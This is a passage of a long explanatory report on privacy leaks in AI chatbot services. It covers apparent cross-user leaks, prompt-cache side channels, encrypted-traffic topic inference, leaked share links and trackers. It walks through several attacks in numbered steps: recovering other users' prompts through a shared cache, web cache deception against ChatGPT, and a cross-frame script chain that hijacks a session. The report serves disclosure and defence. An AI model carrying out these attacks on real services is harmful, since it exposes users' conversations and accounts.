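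The victim saw a normal answer. The only sign was a label beside it, which appeared after ChatGPT had read the data, according to medianet's *Sicherheitslücke in ChatGPT entdeckt* (2026). eSecurity Planet recommends the "Always ask" setting for connected apps. That setting might have interrupted the request to Gmail, but the attacker could also steal the conversation without using an app.

OpenAI confirmed that it had retired the package server, and the channel no longer worked by the time Check Point finished its report. Security Arsenal, a security company's blog, noted no reports of real attacks through the channel. However, according to medianet, Check Point said a later compromise of Hugging Face, the site for sharing models, originated in the same internal service. Check Point said it had demonstrated the weakness before the activity that led to that compromise.

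An older flaw exposed files within a single ChatGPT account. Embrace The Red found that each user had a separate sandbox, but that all the custom GPTs a person used shared that user's sandbox. A GPT made by a stranger could therefore read or overwrite files that the user had given to another GPT. OpenAI fixed this in May 2024.

### Invented text that looks like a leak

In May 2025 a security researcher told OpenAI that its API was returning responses meant for other people. The researcher had been using gpt-4o-transcribe, a speech-to-text model, on recordings close to its 1,500-second limit. Instead of a transcript, the model sometimes returned coherent answers, in various languages, to questions the researcher had never asked.

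One answer was a detailed financial analysis of a little-known company in Kazakhstan. The researcher asked ChatGPT for the same analysis without web search, and it replied that it did not have the company's financial statements. The researcher took this as proof that the text came from another customer's session with web search turned on.

OpenAI first replied in substance on 16 July, a day after the researcher had gone public. It explained that a bug had reduced recordings over certain limits to an empty input. With nothing to transcribe, the model picked a random first token, then a second that fitted the first, and so on until it had written a whole reply. OpenAI had already fixed the bug. The researcher then rechecked the analysis and noticed that most of its figures were suspiciously round, such as 17,000,000 and 25,000,000, and did not match public filings. They withdrew the claim of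 a leak and apologised.

The test with ChatGPT failed because it involved asking for a company's accounts. A model that says it lacks the accounts when asked can still invent them when its input is empty. Chat models learn from enormous numbers of conversations, so when given an empty input they tend to write something that resembles a conversation.

Invented text can also stem from a detail the user has overlooked. In a 2026 case, a user of Claude Sonnet 5 received text about the video game Minecraft during unrelated programming work and suspected that it came from someone else's session. An earlier tool result had listed the files of an installed software package, including one named `minecraft.py`. That file name could explain the text without a leak between users, though it isn't proven to be the cause.

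*Foreign code in agent response* (2026), a report on Cursor's forum, is weak evidence for the same reason. The reply began with the code that the user wanted, then changed to a tutorial for a finance application in a different framework. The user concluded that the tutorial came from someone else's chat. It could have, but the model could also have generated it, since the user described the code as a simple example and models are trained on many such tutorials.

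A developer on Google's forum considered whether Gemini's replies were alike because they were forced into a fixed schema (*generateContent with responseSchema returns content from a different, unrelated prior request*). Another call in the same program used the same schema mechanism, and none of its 14 fields repeated across the same two runs. This counts against the schema as the cause, but the developer could not determine whether a cache or something else in Google's systems was responsible. Repetition alone would also not show that the content belonged to another customer.

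### The Claude reports of June 2026

On 5 June 2026 several developers wrote that Claude's API had sent them answers to other people's prompts. The Chinese technology outlet 新智元's *突发！Claude大面积宕机，用户竟收到“别人的对话* (2026) describes a screenshot of a user's Claude window showing an unrelated task, an article about sport in Colombia. Another user posted that replies were unrelated to the prompts and that, after repeated checks, the fault did not seem to be in their own code.

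Claude was malfunctioning at the time. IsDown's *Elevated errors on many Claude models* (2026), a copy of Anthropic's status updates, shows that Anthropic began investigating at 15:19 UTC and declared the incident resolved at 18:28. The incident affected Opus 4.5 to 4.8 and Sonnet 4.6. Anthropic called the problem "elevated errors" and did not mention any exposure of customer data in its final incident report, according to VPNCentral's *Anthropic Says Claude Model Errors Were Resolved After June 5 Service Disruption* (2026). Two days after the incident, 新智元 reported that Anthropic had neither confirmed nor denied a leak.

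cside, which published on the day itself, based its account on users' screenshots and first-hand reports. It judged them consistent with a mix-up between customers and pointed to the similarity with the 2023 Redis fault, but called this an early interpretation. It did not reproduce the screenshots, since they might contain another customer's data. The company sells software that monitors web pages, including those that display AI output, so it has an interest in the subject.

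Anthropic's description does not settle whether the replies came from other users' conversations. Its updates tracked how often requests succeeded, and a system may well record a success when it delivers a well-formed answer to the wrong person. But a failing service could instead have passed the model an empty or damaged prompt, as OpenAI's transcription service had done a year earlier, and the model would then have written an irrelevant reply that belonged to no one else. The timing makes a fault in Anthropic's systems likely, but the screenshots can't show which kind.

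### A critical rating without a confirmed owner

In *URGENT* (2026), the independent researcher Uzonyi describes getting detailed personal and health information from ChatGPT during ordinary use that did not come from Uzonyi's own account or files. OpenAI receives reports of security flaws through Bugcrowd, a company that runs reward programmes. Bugcrowd's record shows the highest priority (P1), a reward of $2,000 and the status "Resolved".

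A reviewer had closed the first report as not reproducible and asked for proof of impact. After Uzonyi sent further reports, OpenAI and Bugcrowd reopened the case because a broader internal review had confirmed a technical problem that "occurred only in narrow conditions".

Uzonyi gives conflicting accounts of whether OpenAI confirmed that the data was authentic and belonged to another user. The abstract says it did, but the chronology says OpenAI did not confirm this or the presence of personal or health information in the output. The chronology also quotes a more cautious statement from OpenAI, which acknowledged output that "appeared to contain potentially sensitive information" unrelated to the conversation. OpenAI said it had fixed the underlying issue.

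The reward and the fix therefore show that OpenAI found a real bug and took it seriously, but not that anyone's medical records leaked, since the transcription bug was also real and its output was invented. The P1 rating makes a leak more plausible than the text alone does, because a company has less reason to treat nonsense from an empty prompt as critical. Uzonyi proposes two possible causes, a collision in a prompt cache and a search of uploaded files that failed to filter by user, but couldn't test either without access to OpenAI's systems. Although the title mentions prompt injection, Uzonyi writes that no injected instruction was involved.

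Uzonyi argues that reviewers should check a report of this kind against internal records before dismissing it, particularly when the text contains consistent names, dates or diagnostic codes. This is reasonable because such details, though they prove little, can justify a check that only the company can make.

Reproducing an output is not a reliable way to tell whether it contains another user's data. The Redis fault did mix data between users, but only when a request was cancelled at a particular moment, so a second attempt would usually have found nothing. An empty input can repeatedly produce invented conversations even when no data has leaked.

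### Evidence that can settle the question

In the cleanest test, a researcher opens two accounts, puts a random string into one and looks for it in the other. A string of 16 random letters and digits has 36¹⁶ possible values, about 8 × 10²⁴, so a model will not produce it by luck. Check Point's researchers used this type of test on the package-server channel. They wrote a property from one account's sandbox and read it from another account's moments later, without involving a stranger's data.

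The test works well for a channel that is always open but much less well for a rare fault. If each request has a probability p of returning the wrong data, the chance of seeing it at least once in m requests is

1 − (1 − p)ᵐ.

If a fault affects one request in a million, a researcher who sends 10,000 requests would have about a 1% chance of triggering it. The chance of detecting it would be lower, because the misdelivered data would also have to come from the researcher's other account rather than from another customer.

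For rare faults, the company's logs are better evidence. If the suspicious text appears word for word in the record of a request another customer made shortly before, a mix-up is almost certain. A failed search is less conclusive, because some customers have agreements under which the company keeps no text, and a model working from the wrong cached computation would have written something that appears in nobody else's history. To check for this caching fault, the company would have to compare the text with other customers' prompts as well as their replies.

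The supposed owner can also confirm that the information is theirs, but they need to confirm too that they gave it to the chatbot and that it was not public. Otherwise, the model may have repeated accurate facts about them from its training data or a web page. It is better for the company to ask the owner, because the person who received the text would have to search for a stranger using private information that may have leaked.

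The model's own explanation has almost no value as evidence, because the model can't inspect the caches and connections that delivered its input. If a user asks whether a passage came from another session, the model may agree without any basis. GPT-5.5's explanation was similarly unreliable when it attributed an incorrect tool call to the application, although the model had written the call.

Developers can make such an investigation much easier by logging each request. VPNCentral recommends saving the model's name, the status code, the time and the request ID, which the service assigns to each exchange. cside gives similar advice so that developers can tell a model's error from a reply meant for someone else. The company can use the ID to look up the exact exchange, so the developer doesn't have to share what may be a stranger's conversation.

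## Inferring other users' prompts from response times and encrypted traffic

A prompt cache can leak information even when the service delivers every reply to the right user. If Ana and Ben share a cache, Ben may get a faster reply because Ana recently sent a prompt with the same opening, so he can infer something about her prompt from the speed. Someone who can watch the network doesn't need an account, because the size and timing of encrypted messages can reveal what a conversation is about.

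### A faster reply to a repeated opening

A prompt cache stores computation, not finished replies or copies of web pages, so when a prompt begins the same way as an earlier one, the server has to process only the rest. OpenAI's *Prompt Caching 101* explains that its service does this automatically for prompts longer than 1,024 tokens.

Suppose a server processes 10,000 prompt tokens per second and everything else takes 0.05 seconds. Ben sends a prompt of 4,096 tokens. If nobody has sent its opening recently, the cache misses. If Ana has just sent a prompt with the same first 3,891 tokens, it hits, and the server has only 205 tokens left to process:

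- **Miss:** 0.05 + 4,096 / 10,000 ≈ 0.46 seconds
- **Hit:** 0.05 + 205 / 10,000 ≈ 0.07 seconds

A hit means that someone who shares Ben's cache recently sent that exact opening. If he had found a company's supposed secret system prompt online, a hit would suggest that the text is genuine and in use, though he wouldn't learn who sent it. A miss proves little, because the stored computation may have expired or his request may have gone to a different machine. Ben's own request can also put the text in the cache, so a repeated test may only detect his earlier one.

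### Audits of response times

Real response times vary with network and server load, so one fast reply is weak evidence. Gu and colleagues developed a statistical test for this in 2025, and Fahey (2026), in *CacheProbe*, reused it. The tester measures the time to the first token for two sets of prompts, one with new openings and one with openings that another request has just sent. Let F_miss(t) and F_hit(t) be the shares of replies in each set that begin within t seconds. The Kolmogorov–Smirnov statistic is the largest gap between them:

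D = max over t of |F_miss(t) − F_hit(t)|.

D is 0 if the two sets of times have the same distribution and 1 if they don't overlap at all. The tester then calculates p, the probability of a D at least this large if caching made no difference. Fahey followed Gu and colleagues in requiring p to be below 10⁻⁸.

A cached prompt may produce hits only for the account that first sent it, also for other accounts in the same organization, or even for unrelated customers. Gu and colleagues found caches shared among all users at seven API providers, including OpenAI. According to Fahey, most providers have since limited each cache to one account or organization. OpenAI states that it does not share prompt caches between organizations.

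Fahey tested OpenAI, Groq and Fireworks in November and December 2025 and found no cache sharing between accounts that called them directly. Timing was an unreliable signal. Cache hits at Groq were slower than misses on average, and OpenAI's response times did not pass the threshold even within one account. But both services reported how many prompt tokens came from the cache, which showed that caching was working. An attacker can read this number without timing anything.

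### Gateways that pool their customers

OpenRouter is a gateway that offers many companies' models through one account. It normally forwards requests under its own credentials, so a provider sees all of OpenRouter's customers as one organization. Fahey looked for cache hits between two accounts in three arrangements:

| Provider | Direct accounts | OpenRouter's credentials | Each customer's own key through OpenRouter |
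|---|---|---|---|
| Groq | No sharing detected | Hits in all samples that reported a count | No sharing detected |
| Fireworks | No sharing detected | Sharing detected by timing | No sharing detected |
| OpenAI | No sharing detected | Hits in 4.8% of requests | No sharing detected |

OpenRouter acknowledged Fahey's report and asked to see the code. Fahey sent an invitation but got no response.

*KeyPooling* (Sun, Cai and colleagues, 2026) uses a more direct test with four requests. Ana sends a long random text, Ben sends the same text, Ana repeats it, and Ben sends an unrelated one. In one result, the provider reported 0, 1,408, 1,408 and 0 cached tokens. The second number shows the leak, because it would be 0 if Ana and Ben had separate caches. The third confirms that the cache was working, and the fourth rules out a service that reports hits for everything.

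The team ran five open-source gateway programs with two customers behind one provider credential. All five leaked with OpenAI's models, and with Anthropic's when requests turned caching on. None gave each customer a separate credential by default. On OpenRouter, the team examined 28 popular models from a ranking for the week ending 1 August 2026. Twelve leaked between accounts on at least one route, one did not leak on the route tested, eleven gave inconclusive results and four were not tested. The twelve accounted for 33.7% of the traffic to the 28 models, but the share of requests exposed is unknown because a model can have several routes.

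A large gateway can't fully solve this through careful configuration. OpenAI separates caches by organization and creates additional organizations only on request. Anthropic's direct API separates them by workspace and allows 100 workspaces per organization. A gateway with more customers than separate caches has to make some customers share a cache.

### Reading a prompt one token at a time

All of these audits confirm a text the tester already has. To read an unknown prompt, an attacker would have to start from a known opening and guess what follows. With k candidates for each of n positions, there are kⁿ complete texts to try, but guessing one token at a time takes at most n × k guesses. For eight positions with four candidates each, that is 65,536 texts compared with 32 guesses.

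Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *I Know What You Asked*, demonstrated this on SGLang, an open-source program for serving models. Their attack relied on the order of replies instead of their speed. When requests are waiting, SGLang first serves those whose openings match the most cached tokens. Suppose Ana's prompt begins "Draft a letter to my landlord", each word is one token, and the attacker knows the first five:

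1. The attacker sends many identical filler requests with the five known words and an unlikely sixth. The server starts on some of them, which puts their text in the cache.
2. While the others wait, the attacker sends three guesses for the sixth word, "boss", "doctor" and "landlord", followed by more fillers.
3. The fillers and the "landlord" request now match six cached tokens. The other two guesses match five, so the server moves them to the back.
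4. The reply to "landlord" arrives between the two groups of fillers. The attacker adds the word to the known text and starts on the seventh.

The attacker runs a second language model to suggest guesses. On a server with one graphics processor, the attack recovered at least part of the prompt in 95% of cases without prior knowledge. When the attacker knew the template and only had to find what the user had filled in, the figure was 99%. In one health template, the attacker found the user's gender, age, weight and height in 60 guesses. An unusual word could take thousands of guesses, such as 4,093 for "Frank" in a question about the Frankish Kingdom.

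These counts leave out the fillers. The server processed up to 16 requests at once, and the attack needed more than 16 fillers both before and after each batch of guesses. In the tests that counted guesses, each batch contained only one guess, so the attack sent more than 30 times as many requests as were counted.

The attack also requires that strangers share a cache, that their requests reach the same processor, and that the server prioritises requests whose openings are already cached and accepts large numbers of tiny requests. Wu and colleagues tested only a local server and left public clouds for later work. The recovered texts became shorter once more than 200 simulated users were active, because new requests filled the memory and pushed out the victim's prompt. An outsider cannot use the attack if the provider keeps a separate cache for each organization.

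Gateways can make strangers share a cache again. Sun and colleagues recovered a short secret from a test victim through a commercial gateway. The victim stored eight words, each chosen from the same four options, after a context that the attacker knew. The attacker identified all eight words from the reported token counts, using 258 requests, about half of them for a control run without the victim. The secret contained 16 bits, roughly as much information as three random letters or digits.

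Two attempts with eight candidates per position had to stop when one guess in each missed the cache. The team estimates that a list of 2,048 words would require 98,370 requests for eight positions. Some routes also report cached tokens only in blocks of 128, which hides most one-token gains. Sun and colleagues found no commercial setting in which they could reliably extract arbitrary text. Researchers have shown that attackers can confirm a guessed prompt on commercial services, but they have recovered unknown prompts there only under very favourable conditions. All of these experiments used test prompts, not those of real customers.

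### The cost of separate caches

Giving each customer a separate cache prevents these tests but gives up legitimate savings. For example, users of the same coding agent all send the same long instructions and tool definitions. Sun and colleagues modelled this with 5,713 requests based on public conversations. Complete separation raised costs to between 2.29 and 3.14 times those of a shared cache.

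A design with less overhead shares the public opening of a prompt across customers and separates them from the first private token onward. It added only 1.7% to 2.5% overhead. The operator has to classify the text correctly and treat anything inserted for a particular user as private. The split also has to fall on a block boundary, or private tokens in the same block as public ones would remain shared.

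A gateway can't build this protection alone. In a trial with OpenAI's API, a gateway derived a different cache key from each customer's login, which stopped the leak and still let customers reuse their own prompts. But OpenAI documents the key as a way to route requests, and Fahey warns that two customers' requests could still reach the same server. Sun and colleagues found no provider that offered gateways an enforced label for each customer. Until one does, customers with sensitive prompts can call the provider directly or give the gateway their own API key.

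Operators who serve models with vLLM can already keep caches separate with a value attached to each request. *Isonomy* (2026) proposes a design that aims to protect every request from timing leaks while running nearly as fast as full cache sharing.

### What encrypted traffic reveals

An internet provider, a government or someone on the same Wi-Fi network may be able to see a user's encrypted traffic. Encryption hides the text but not its length, because the encrypted data is longer than the original by a fixed amount. Chatbots usually stream a reply in small pieces as the model writes it, so the observer sees a sequence of sizes and pauses. Soleimani, Jia and colleagues (2025) showed that speculative decoding, in which a server drafts several tokens quickly and then checks them, makes this pattern depend on the text.

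McDonald and Bar Or (2025), in *Whisper Leak*, tested whether such patterns reveal a conversation's topic. The two Microsoft researchers chose the legality of money laundering and wrote 100 versions of a question about it. They sent each version up to 100 times to 28 models, along with 11,716 unrelated questions, and recorded the encrypted replies. Then they trained classifiers to recognise the topic from packet sizes and timing, and tested them on 20 versions they had held back.

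The score is the area under the curve that plots precision against recall, and a perfect classifier scores 100%. Precision is the share of flagged conversations that are about the topic, and recall is the share of conversations about the topic that the classifier flags. Scores were at least 97% for 17 of the 28 models, including 98.6% for GPT-4o mini. They were 91.2% for Claude 3 Haiku, 82% to 84% for the Gemini models, and 71% to 78% for Amazon's Nova models.

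The classifier recognises a topic that the observer chose in advance and doesn't recover any of the user's words. An observer interested in protests, for instance, would have to collect examples and train a classifier for that topic.

### False alarms when the topic is rare

The experiment contained almost as many questions about money laundering as about everything else. In real traffic such a topic is rare, so even a low false-alarm rate can produce mostly false alarms. If there are 10,000 other conversations for each one on the topic, r is the recall and f is the share of other conversations wrongly flagged, then

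precision = r / (r + 10,000 f).

McDonald and Bar Or projected that, for 17 models, an observer could identify one in five conversations on the topic without a single false alarm (100% precision at 20% recall). Judging by the published figures, however, each test seems to have included only about 2,340 unrelated questions, a fifth of the total. One false alarm among them would reduce the projected precision at 50% recall from 100% to 10.5%, exactly the figure listed for four of the models. The 100% therefore means that the classifier raised no false alarms on roughly 2,340 questions, which is too few to establish how it would perform on millions.

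Microsoft's own account of the research, *Whisper Leak* (2025), also cautions that these figures are projections. An observer could get better results than the researchers by collecting more data or following a user through several conversations. In tests on GPT-4o, the classifiers kept improving as the researchers added training data.

### Padding and its limits

McDonald and Bar Or began notifying providers in June 2025. OpenAI and xAI introduced protections that August, Mistral in September and Microsoft in October. Other providers declined or did not answer. OpenAI added a field of random text of varying length to each piece of a streamed reply, so that the size of the piece no longer reveals the length of the token. Microsoft adopted the same method, and Mistral a similar one.

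The researchers measured padding on GPT-4o mini as served by Microsoft, and simulated two other measures on traffic from OpenAI's version:

| Measure | Score without it | Score with it | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Random padding | 97.5% | 92.9% | Larger messages |
| Sending five tokens at a time | 98.2% | 94.8% | Text appears in bursts |
| Adding fake messages | 98.1% | 93.3% | Two to three times the traffic |

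Microsoft considers the attack no longer a practical risk on its padded service. A score of 92.9% doesn't necessarily contradict this, because a classifier can score about that high and still be of little use for detecting a rare topic. Before the fix, a classifier scored 90.1% against GPT-4o on Microsoft's service, but its projected precision was only 1.1% at 5% recall. However, Microsoft was judging its own fix against the classifiers available at the time.

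Sending messages of equal size at a constant rate would protect users better, but it takes much more bandwidth and slows replies. Microsoft advises concerned users to avoid sensitive topics on untrusted networks, turn off streaming where possible or use a virtual private network (VPN), which sends their traffic through another company's servers. Without streaming, an observer can still see roughly how long the reply is. A VPN prevents the local network from seeing which chatbot the user is contacting, but the VPN company can observe the encrypted traffic.

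## Leaks through share links, the chat page and outside companies

Pressing ChatGPT's share button publishes a copy of the conversation at a web address containing a long random ID. Anyone with the address can read the copy without logging in. Strangers can't guess the ID, so the chat stays reasonably private as long as only the intended readers have the address. In 2025, search engines listed many such addresses, although nobody had broken into any of the chatbot services.

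### Shared chats in search results

ChatGPT's share window had a checkbox that made a chat "discoverable" by search engines. At the end of July 2025 the magazine Fast Company searched Google for ChatGPT's share addresses and found nearly 4,500 conversations, some about health or other intimate matters. OpenAI removed the option within about a day. Its security chief, Dane Stuckey, called the option a "short-lived experiment" that gave people too many chances to share something by accident, and said OpenAI was working to get the pages out of search results. By then a researcher had copied nearly 100,000 shared chats, according to the news site 404 Media, and removing the pages from Google did not delete those copies.

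Grok, the chatbot made by xAI, had no such checkbox. Its share button created a link that search engines could list, without warning users. Forbes reported in August 2025 that Google had indexed more than 370,000 Grok conversations, and that xAI had not answered its questions. The following month Forbes found just under 600 shared conversations with Claude. Anthropic said that it blocked search engines' crawlers from these pages, and that the links had turned up because people had posted them elsewhere.

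Both halves of Anthropic's reply can be true. A website's owner can ask crawlers not to read certain pages, but a search engine may still list the address of an unread page if it finds a link to it on another site. The owner can also add a label inside a page asking search engines to leave it out of their results, but a crawler that is blocked from reading the page won't see the label.

The three counts come from different searches on different dates, so they don't show which service exposed the largest share of its chats. They also include chats that people were happy to publish. The reports do show that many users treated a share link as a private message to a few people, although it opened a public page.

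### A share link that opened every chat

*One Public Share Link Unlocks Full Takeover* (mdpsec, 22 May 2026) reports that a share link to a single AI chat on the site of an unnamed major US news publication gave access to everything the chat's owner had ever discussed with the assistant. This is one researcher's account, and it does not mention a fix.

The researcher found two faults that were much worse together. When someone opened a shared chat, the site's server sent their browser the owner's permanent user ID along with the text. The part of the server that handled chat histories accepted this ID in place of a login.

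The researcher tested the flaw using their own account as the victim and a second browser, which was not logged in, as the attacker. From the second browser, they listed all the victim's chats and read one that the victim had never shared. They also added a conversation to the victim's history, where it looked like one the victim had written, and then deleted the whole history. They sent thirty requests in a row without hitting a rate limit.

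AskTheCode, the ChatGPT plugin that issued a login code for any member ID, had the same flaw three years earlier. mdpsec recommends that the server give access to a history only through a logged-in session, and that a share ID unlock only its own conversation. User IDs on this site never changed, so deleting a shared chat would not have protected its owner if a stranger had already recorded the owner's ID.

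### Private replies stored as public files

Large websites keep copies of their public files, such as logos and style sheets, on servers close to their users. Such a cache gives the stored copy to anyone who asks for it, so it must never store a reply meant for one person. Web cache deception is an attack that gets it to do so. The attack exploits an address that the cache and the application interpret differently:

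1. The attacker takes the address at which ChatGPT's page fetches the user's login details, and adds the name of a style sheet that doesn't exist.
2. A logged-in victim clicks the resulting link, and the browser attaches the victim's cookie.
3. The application ignores the added name and replies with the victim's name, e-mail address and access token.
4. The cache sees an address that ends like a style sheet's, so it stores the reply as a public file.
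5. The attacker opens the same address without logging in and receives the stored copy. With the token, the attacker can take over the account.

Gal Nagli, the head of the security company Shockwave, found this flaw in ChatGPT in March 2023, days after the Redis fault. Arghire reports in *OpenAI Patches Account Takeover Vulnerabilities in ChatGPT* that OpenAI quickly added a rule to stop the cache from storing replies from that address. The rule was a regular expression, a pattern for matching text.

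Ayoub Fathi, another security researcher, got around the fix twice. Fathi first aimed the attack at a different part of ChatGPT's API, which the rule did not cover, and obtained a user's conversation titles. Fathi then found a way to write the original address so that it no longer matched the pattern but still worked. This method worked on all of ChatGPT's APIs and could expose whole chats. Fathi helped OpenAI close the remaining gaps. OpenAI had no reward programme at the time, so it paid neither researcher.

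The problem returned through shared chats. In *ChatGPT Account Takeover* (2024), the researcher Harel explained that the cache now stored everything whose address began with the path for shared conversations, however the address ended. Harel followed this path with an encoded instruction to go up to the parent folder, which the application decoded but the cache did not.

| Version | What the cache saw | What the application returned |
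|---|---|---|
| Nagli, March 2023 | A style sheet | The victim's login details |
| Fathi, after the first fix | A style sheet at an address that the new rule missed | Conversation titles, then login details and whole chats |
| Harel, 2024 | A shared conversation | The victim's login details |

OpenAI's first fix listed what the cache should not store, so an attacker only needed to find one address that the list missed. It is safer for the application to label every private reply "do not store" and for the cache to follow that label whatever the address. The application has already checked whether the user is logged in, which the cache could only infer from the address.

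### From a shared graph to the reader's account

A shared chat can also be dangerous to the person who opens it, because ChatGPT builds the page from someone else's content. Imperva's earlier attack ran a script through shared conversations. *Do the Math* (Goyal, 2026) described a new way to do this, which the research team at security company Parameter had found that October.

The attack began with ChatGPT's HTML preview, the feature that Check Point had used to bypass Lockdown Mode. The preview runs in a restricted frame with its own web address, so the browser treats it as a different website and stops its code from reading the surrounding ChatGPT page. Browsers still let the frame and the page exchange messages if both cooperate, but the receiving page is supposed to check who sent each message.

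Parameter's shared chat contained a preview and an ordinary interactive graph. It worked in these steps:

1. The victim opens the shared chat while logged in to ChatGPT. To draw the graph, ChatGPT loads MathLive, a library for mathematical notation, into the main page. MathLive also begins to listen for messages about its on-screen keyboard.
2. Code in the preview sends MathLive two messages. One replaces the layout of the keyboard with HTML from the attacker, and the other tells MathLive to show the keyboard.
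3. MathLive accepts both without checking the sender, and inserts the HTML into the main page without checking what it contains.
4. The HTML creates another frame. Because the main page created this frame and put no restrictions on it, the browser treats it as part of ChatGPT's own website.
5. The new frame loads a script from YouTube, which ChatGPT's rules allow. One of YouTube's services repeats part of the requested address at the start of its reply, so the attacker can put code in the address and get it back as a script from YouTube.
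6. The code runs as the victim and can make any request that ChatGPT's own page could make.

In Parameter's test, the code read the token for the victim's session, according to the German site KIberblick (2026). It then fetched the list of recent chats, opened a private one and sent an excerpt to an outside server. Goyal writes that the same access would have let an attacker change the account. The team ran the test between separate accounts. According to The Hacker News' *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (2026), Parameter reported no use of the flaw against real users.

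The team needed several attempts to fit the attack into a single link. The first version sent its messages from a ChatGPT app, which the victim would have had to connect. The second used an attached HTML file, but when the team shared that chat, the graph that listened for the messages disappeared from the public copy. The attack worked once both the graph and the preview were part of the conversation. At first the victim also had to click the preview button. In a later version the preview opened automatically, and the code ran about four and a half seconds after the victim opened the link.

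### Protections that worked separately

Several protections did exactly what their designers intended:

| Protection | What it prevented | What it still allowed |
|---|---|---|
| A separate web address for the preview | Reading the main page from the preview | Sending messages to the main page |
| The browser's treatment of inserted HTML | Running script tags added in this way | Creating a frame that loads its own script |
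| ChatGPT's limits on script sources | Running code written directly into the page | Loading scripts from YouTube |
| YouTube's check of the request | Accepting an invalid request | Repeating the attacker's text in front of the error message |

Each one depended on something that another part of the system did not provide. The preview's isolation protects the main page only if that page ignores messages from untrusted sources. MathLive accepts every message, which does little harm on a page where all the code comes from the same company, but ChatGPT's page also contained frames with code that anyone could have written. Permission to load scripts from YouTube is harmless until an attacker can add HTML that loads one. A tester who examined only the preview would have found that it could not reach the main page, and one who examined only the graph would have found no attacker who could send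 it a message.

Parameter reported the flaw on 18 October 2026. According to the Ukrainian site InternetUA (2026), OpenAI confirmed it three days later and raised its severity to P1. By 26 October, both versions of ChatGPT's web page then in use rejected the messages. This was a better fix than only blocking scripts from YouTube, which would still have let the preview insert HTML into the main page. An attacker might then have found another permitted source of scripts.

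OpenAI paid a reward of $5,000, which Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, considered a bit low for such a serious flaw. The attack did not require users to install anything. InternetUA passes on the advice to open links from unknown sources in a private browser tab without logging in. That would have stopped this attack, because there would have been no session for the code to use.

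### Titles and prompts sent to trackers

Some chatbot pages send parts of people's conversations to other companies without any attack taking place. Like most commercial websites, many chatbots load tracking scripts from other companies to count visitors and measure how well advertisements work. These scripts normally report the address and title of each page a visitor opens. A chatbot typically gives each conversation its own page and uses the conversation's title as the page title, so the script may report something like "Anxiety and trouble sleeping".

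Bekos, Tsouvalas and colleagues (2026), in *Penny for Your Prompts*, measured this on 42 chat platforms between 6 and 20 May 2026. They created accounts, typed the same prepared questions on each general-purpose platform, moved between chats and recorded everything the browser sent. For specialised platforms, they wrote questions on the platform's subject, such as one about immigration status for legal assistants. They then searched the traffic to trackers for the exact prompts and titles.

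| | General-purpose platforms | Education, health and legal platforms |
|---|---|---|
| Tested | 25 | 17 |
| Sent conversation titles to trackers | 13 | 8 |
| Sent verbatim prompts to trackers | 4 | 5 |
| Sent a title or prompt and also the user's e-mail address | 11 | 8 |
| Sent both to the same company | 8 | 7 |

In total, 21 platforms sent titles and nine sent prompts. Google and Meta received the most. On the general-purpose platforms, the team counted 230 requests to Google and about 55 to Meta that contained a title or prompt.

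An e-mail address can link an anonymous record to a named person. The legal assistant AI Lawyer sent the conversation's title and the user's e-mail address to Meta and ByteDance in the same request. Many platforms sent a hash of the address instead. This protects users very little, because a company that already has the address can compute the same hash, as with AskTheCode's member IDs.

The team studied nine general-purpose platforms with a modified browser that logs every operation a script performs, to find out how the text reached the trackers. All nine leaked a title when the user went back to an earlier chat, because this counts as opening a new page. Six had already leaked a title or prompt when the user submitted a question.

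The prompts leaked by two routes. You.com put the user's question into the page's URL, which advertising scripts routinely report. ZenoChat and Writesonic used Microsoft Clarity, a tool that records visits so that site owners can replay them. Clarity reads the text shown on the page and anything the user types into the page's fields, so it captured the question before the chatbot had given the chat a title.

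Bekos and colleagues conclude that most of this was unintentional. The platforms installed ordinary tools with default settings. In their privacy notices, they disclose that they collect page views and clicks, but not that this data can contain the subject of a conversation. Several platforms also promise not to share data for targeted advertising, although advertising scripts were running on their pages.

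The team connected from the eastern United States and accepted every cookie request, so users who are elsewhere or refuse tracking may send less data. The recordings show what reached the trackers' servers, but not whether anyone there read it or used it for advertising. ChatGPT had been sending titles to Meta and e-mail addresses to Google, but both it and Grok removed their trackers before the researchers submitted their paper. The team notified the other platforms. TheLawGPT fixed the leak directly, four others passed the report to their staff and two more acknowledged it.

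A user can prevent these leaks with a browser extension that blocks tracking scripts. The platforms could also use page titles that don't describe the conversation. This would stop most of the title leaks, but not leaks through a tool like Clarity, which reads the text itself.

Data held by an analytics company can also leak a second time. In November 2025 an intruder copied customer data from Mixpanel, which OpenAI used to analyse visits to its developer site. OpenAI's *What to know about a recent Mixpanel security incident* (2025) first described the victims as API users, and later clarified that they also included a limited number of ChatGPT users who had submitted help requests or logged in to the developer site. The stolen data included names and e-mail addresses but no chats.

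### Planted credentials at model providers

Other outside companies receive the whole prompt because they run the model. A developer who calls an open-weight model through a gateway such as OpenRouter may not know which company is running it, or how many others handle the request on the way.

HD Moore, the chief research officer of the security company Dragos, looked for leaks along these routes by planting canary tokens in about two million prompts (Moore, *Three breaches, endless leaks*, 2026). A canary token is a fake secret that alerts its owner when someone uses it. Moore's were mostly web addresses and login keys for empty accounts at Amazon's cloud service, AWS. Each secret went into one prompt, which the team sent once to one provider (Faisal, *Researcher Planted 2 Million Fake Secrets in AI Prompts*, 2026). If anyone used a key, the team therefore knew which prompt it had come from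 and which provider had received it.

This resembles the test in which a researcher puts a random string into one account and looks for it in another, but it can catch thieves as well as faults. It will probably miss many thieves, because someone who copied a key without trying it would leave no trace, and someone interested only in medical questions would have no reason to try it.

Unlike most research on ChatGPT's flaws, the study found real thefts. Between July and November 2026, attackers stole data from at least three providers, none of which knew until Moore's team told them. The Hacker News' *OpenRouter Drops 3 Providers After Researchers Catch Months of Prompt Theft* (2026) describes the largest case. During several short periods in late October, the attacker copied every request that Dragos sent to one provider. These included requests that the provider had rejected before any model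 processed them, so the attacker was probably copying traffic as it entered the system. In some cases the attacker tried the stolen keys within hours, searched the accounts for more secrets and attempted to create new users to keep access. Dragos considers it almost certain that the attacker also copied other customers' prompts, because the providers processed them alongside the planted ones.

Some prompts leaked without a break-in because sellers logged them. These sellers offered the lowest prices on a marketplace where companies and individuals compete to run models for customers. One seller, working from a home connection in France, took passwords from two prompts and typed login attempts by hand. The same person tried several planted keys. One of those keys had reached the marketplace through another gateway, which forwarded some of its traffic there without its customers' knowledge.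 The gateway's operator has told Dragos that it stopped doing this.

### Together AI and Phala

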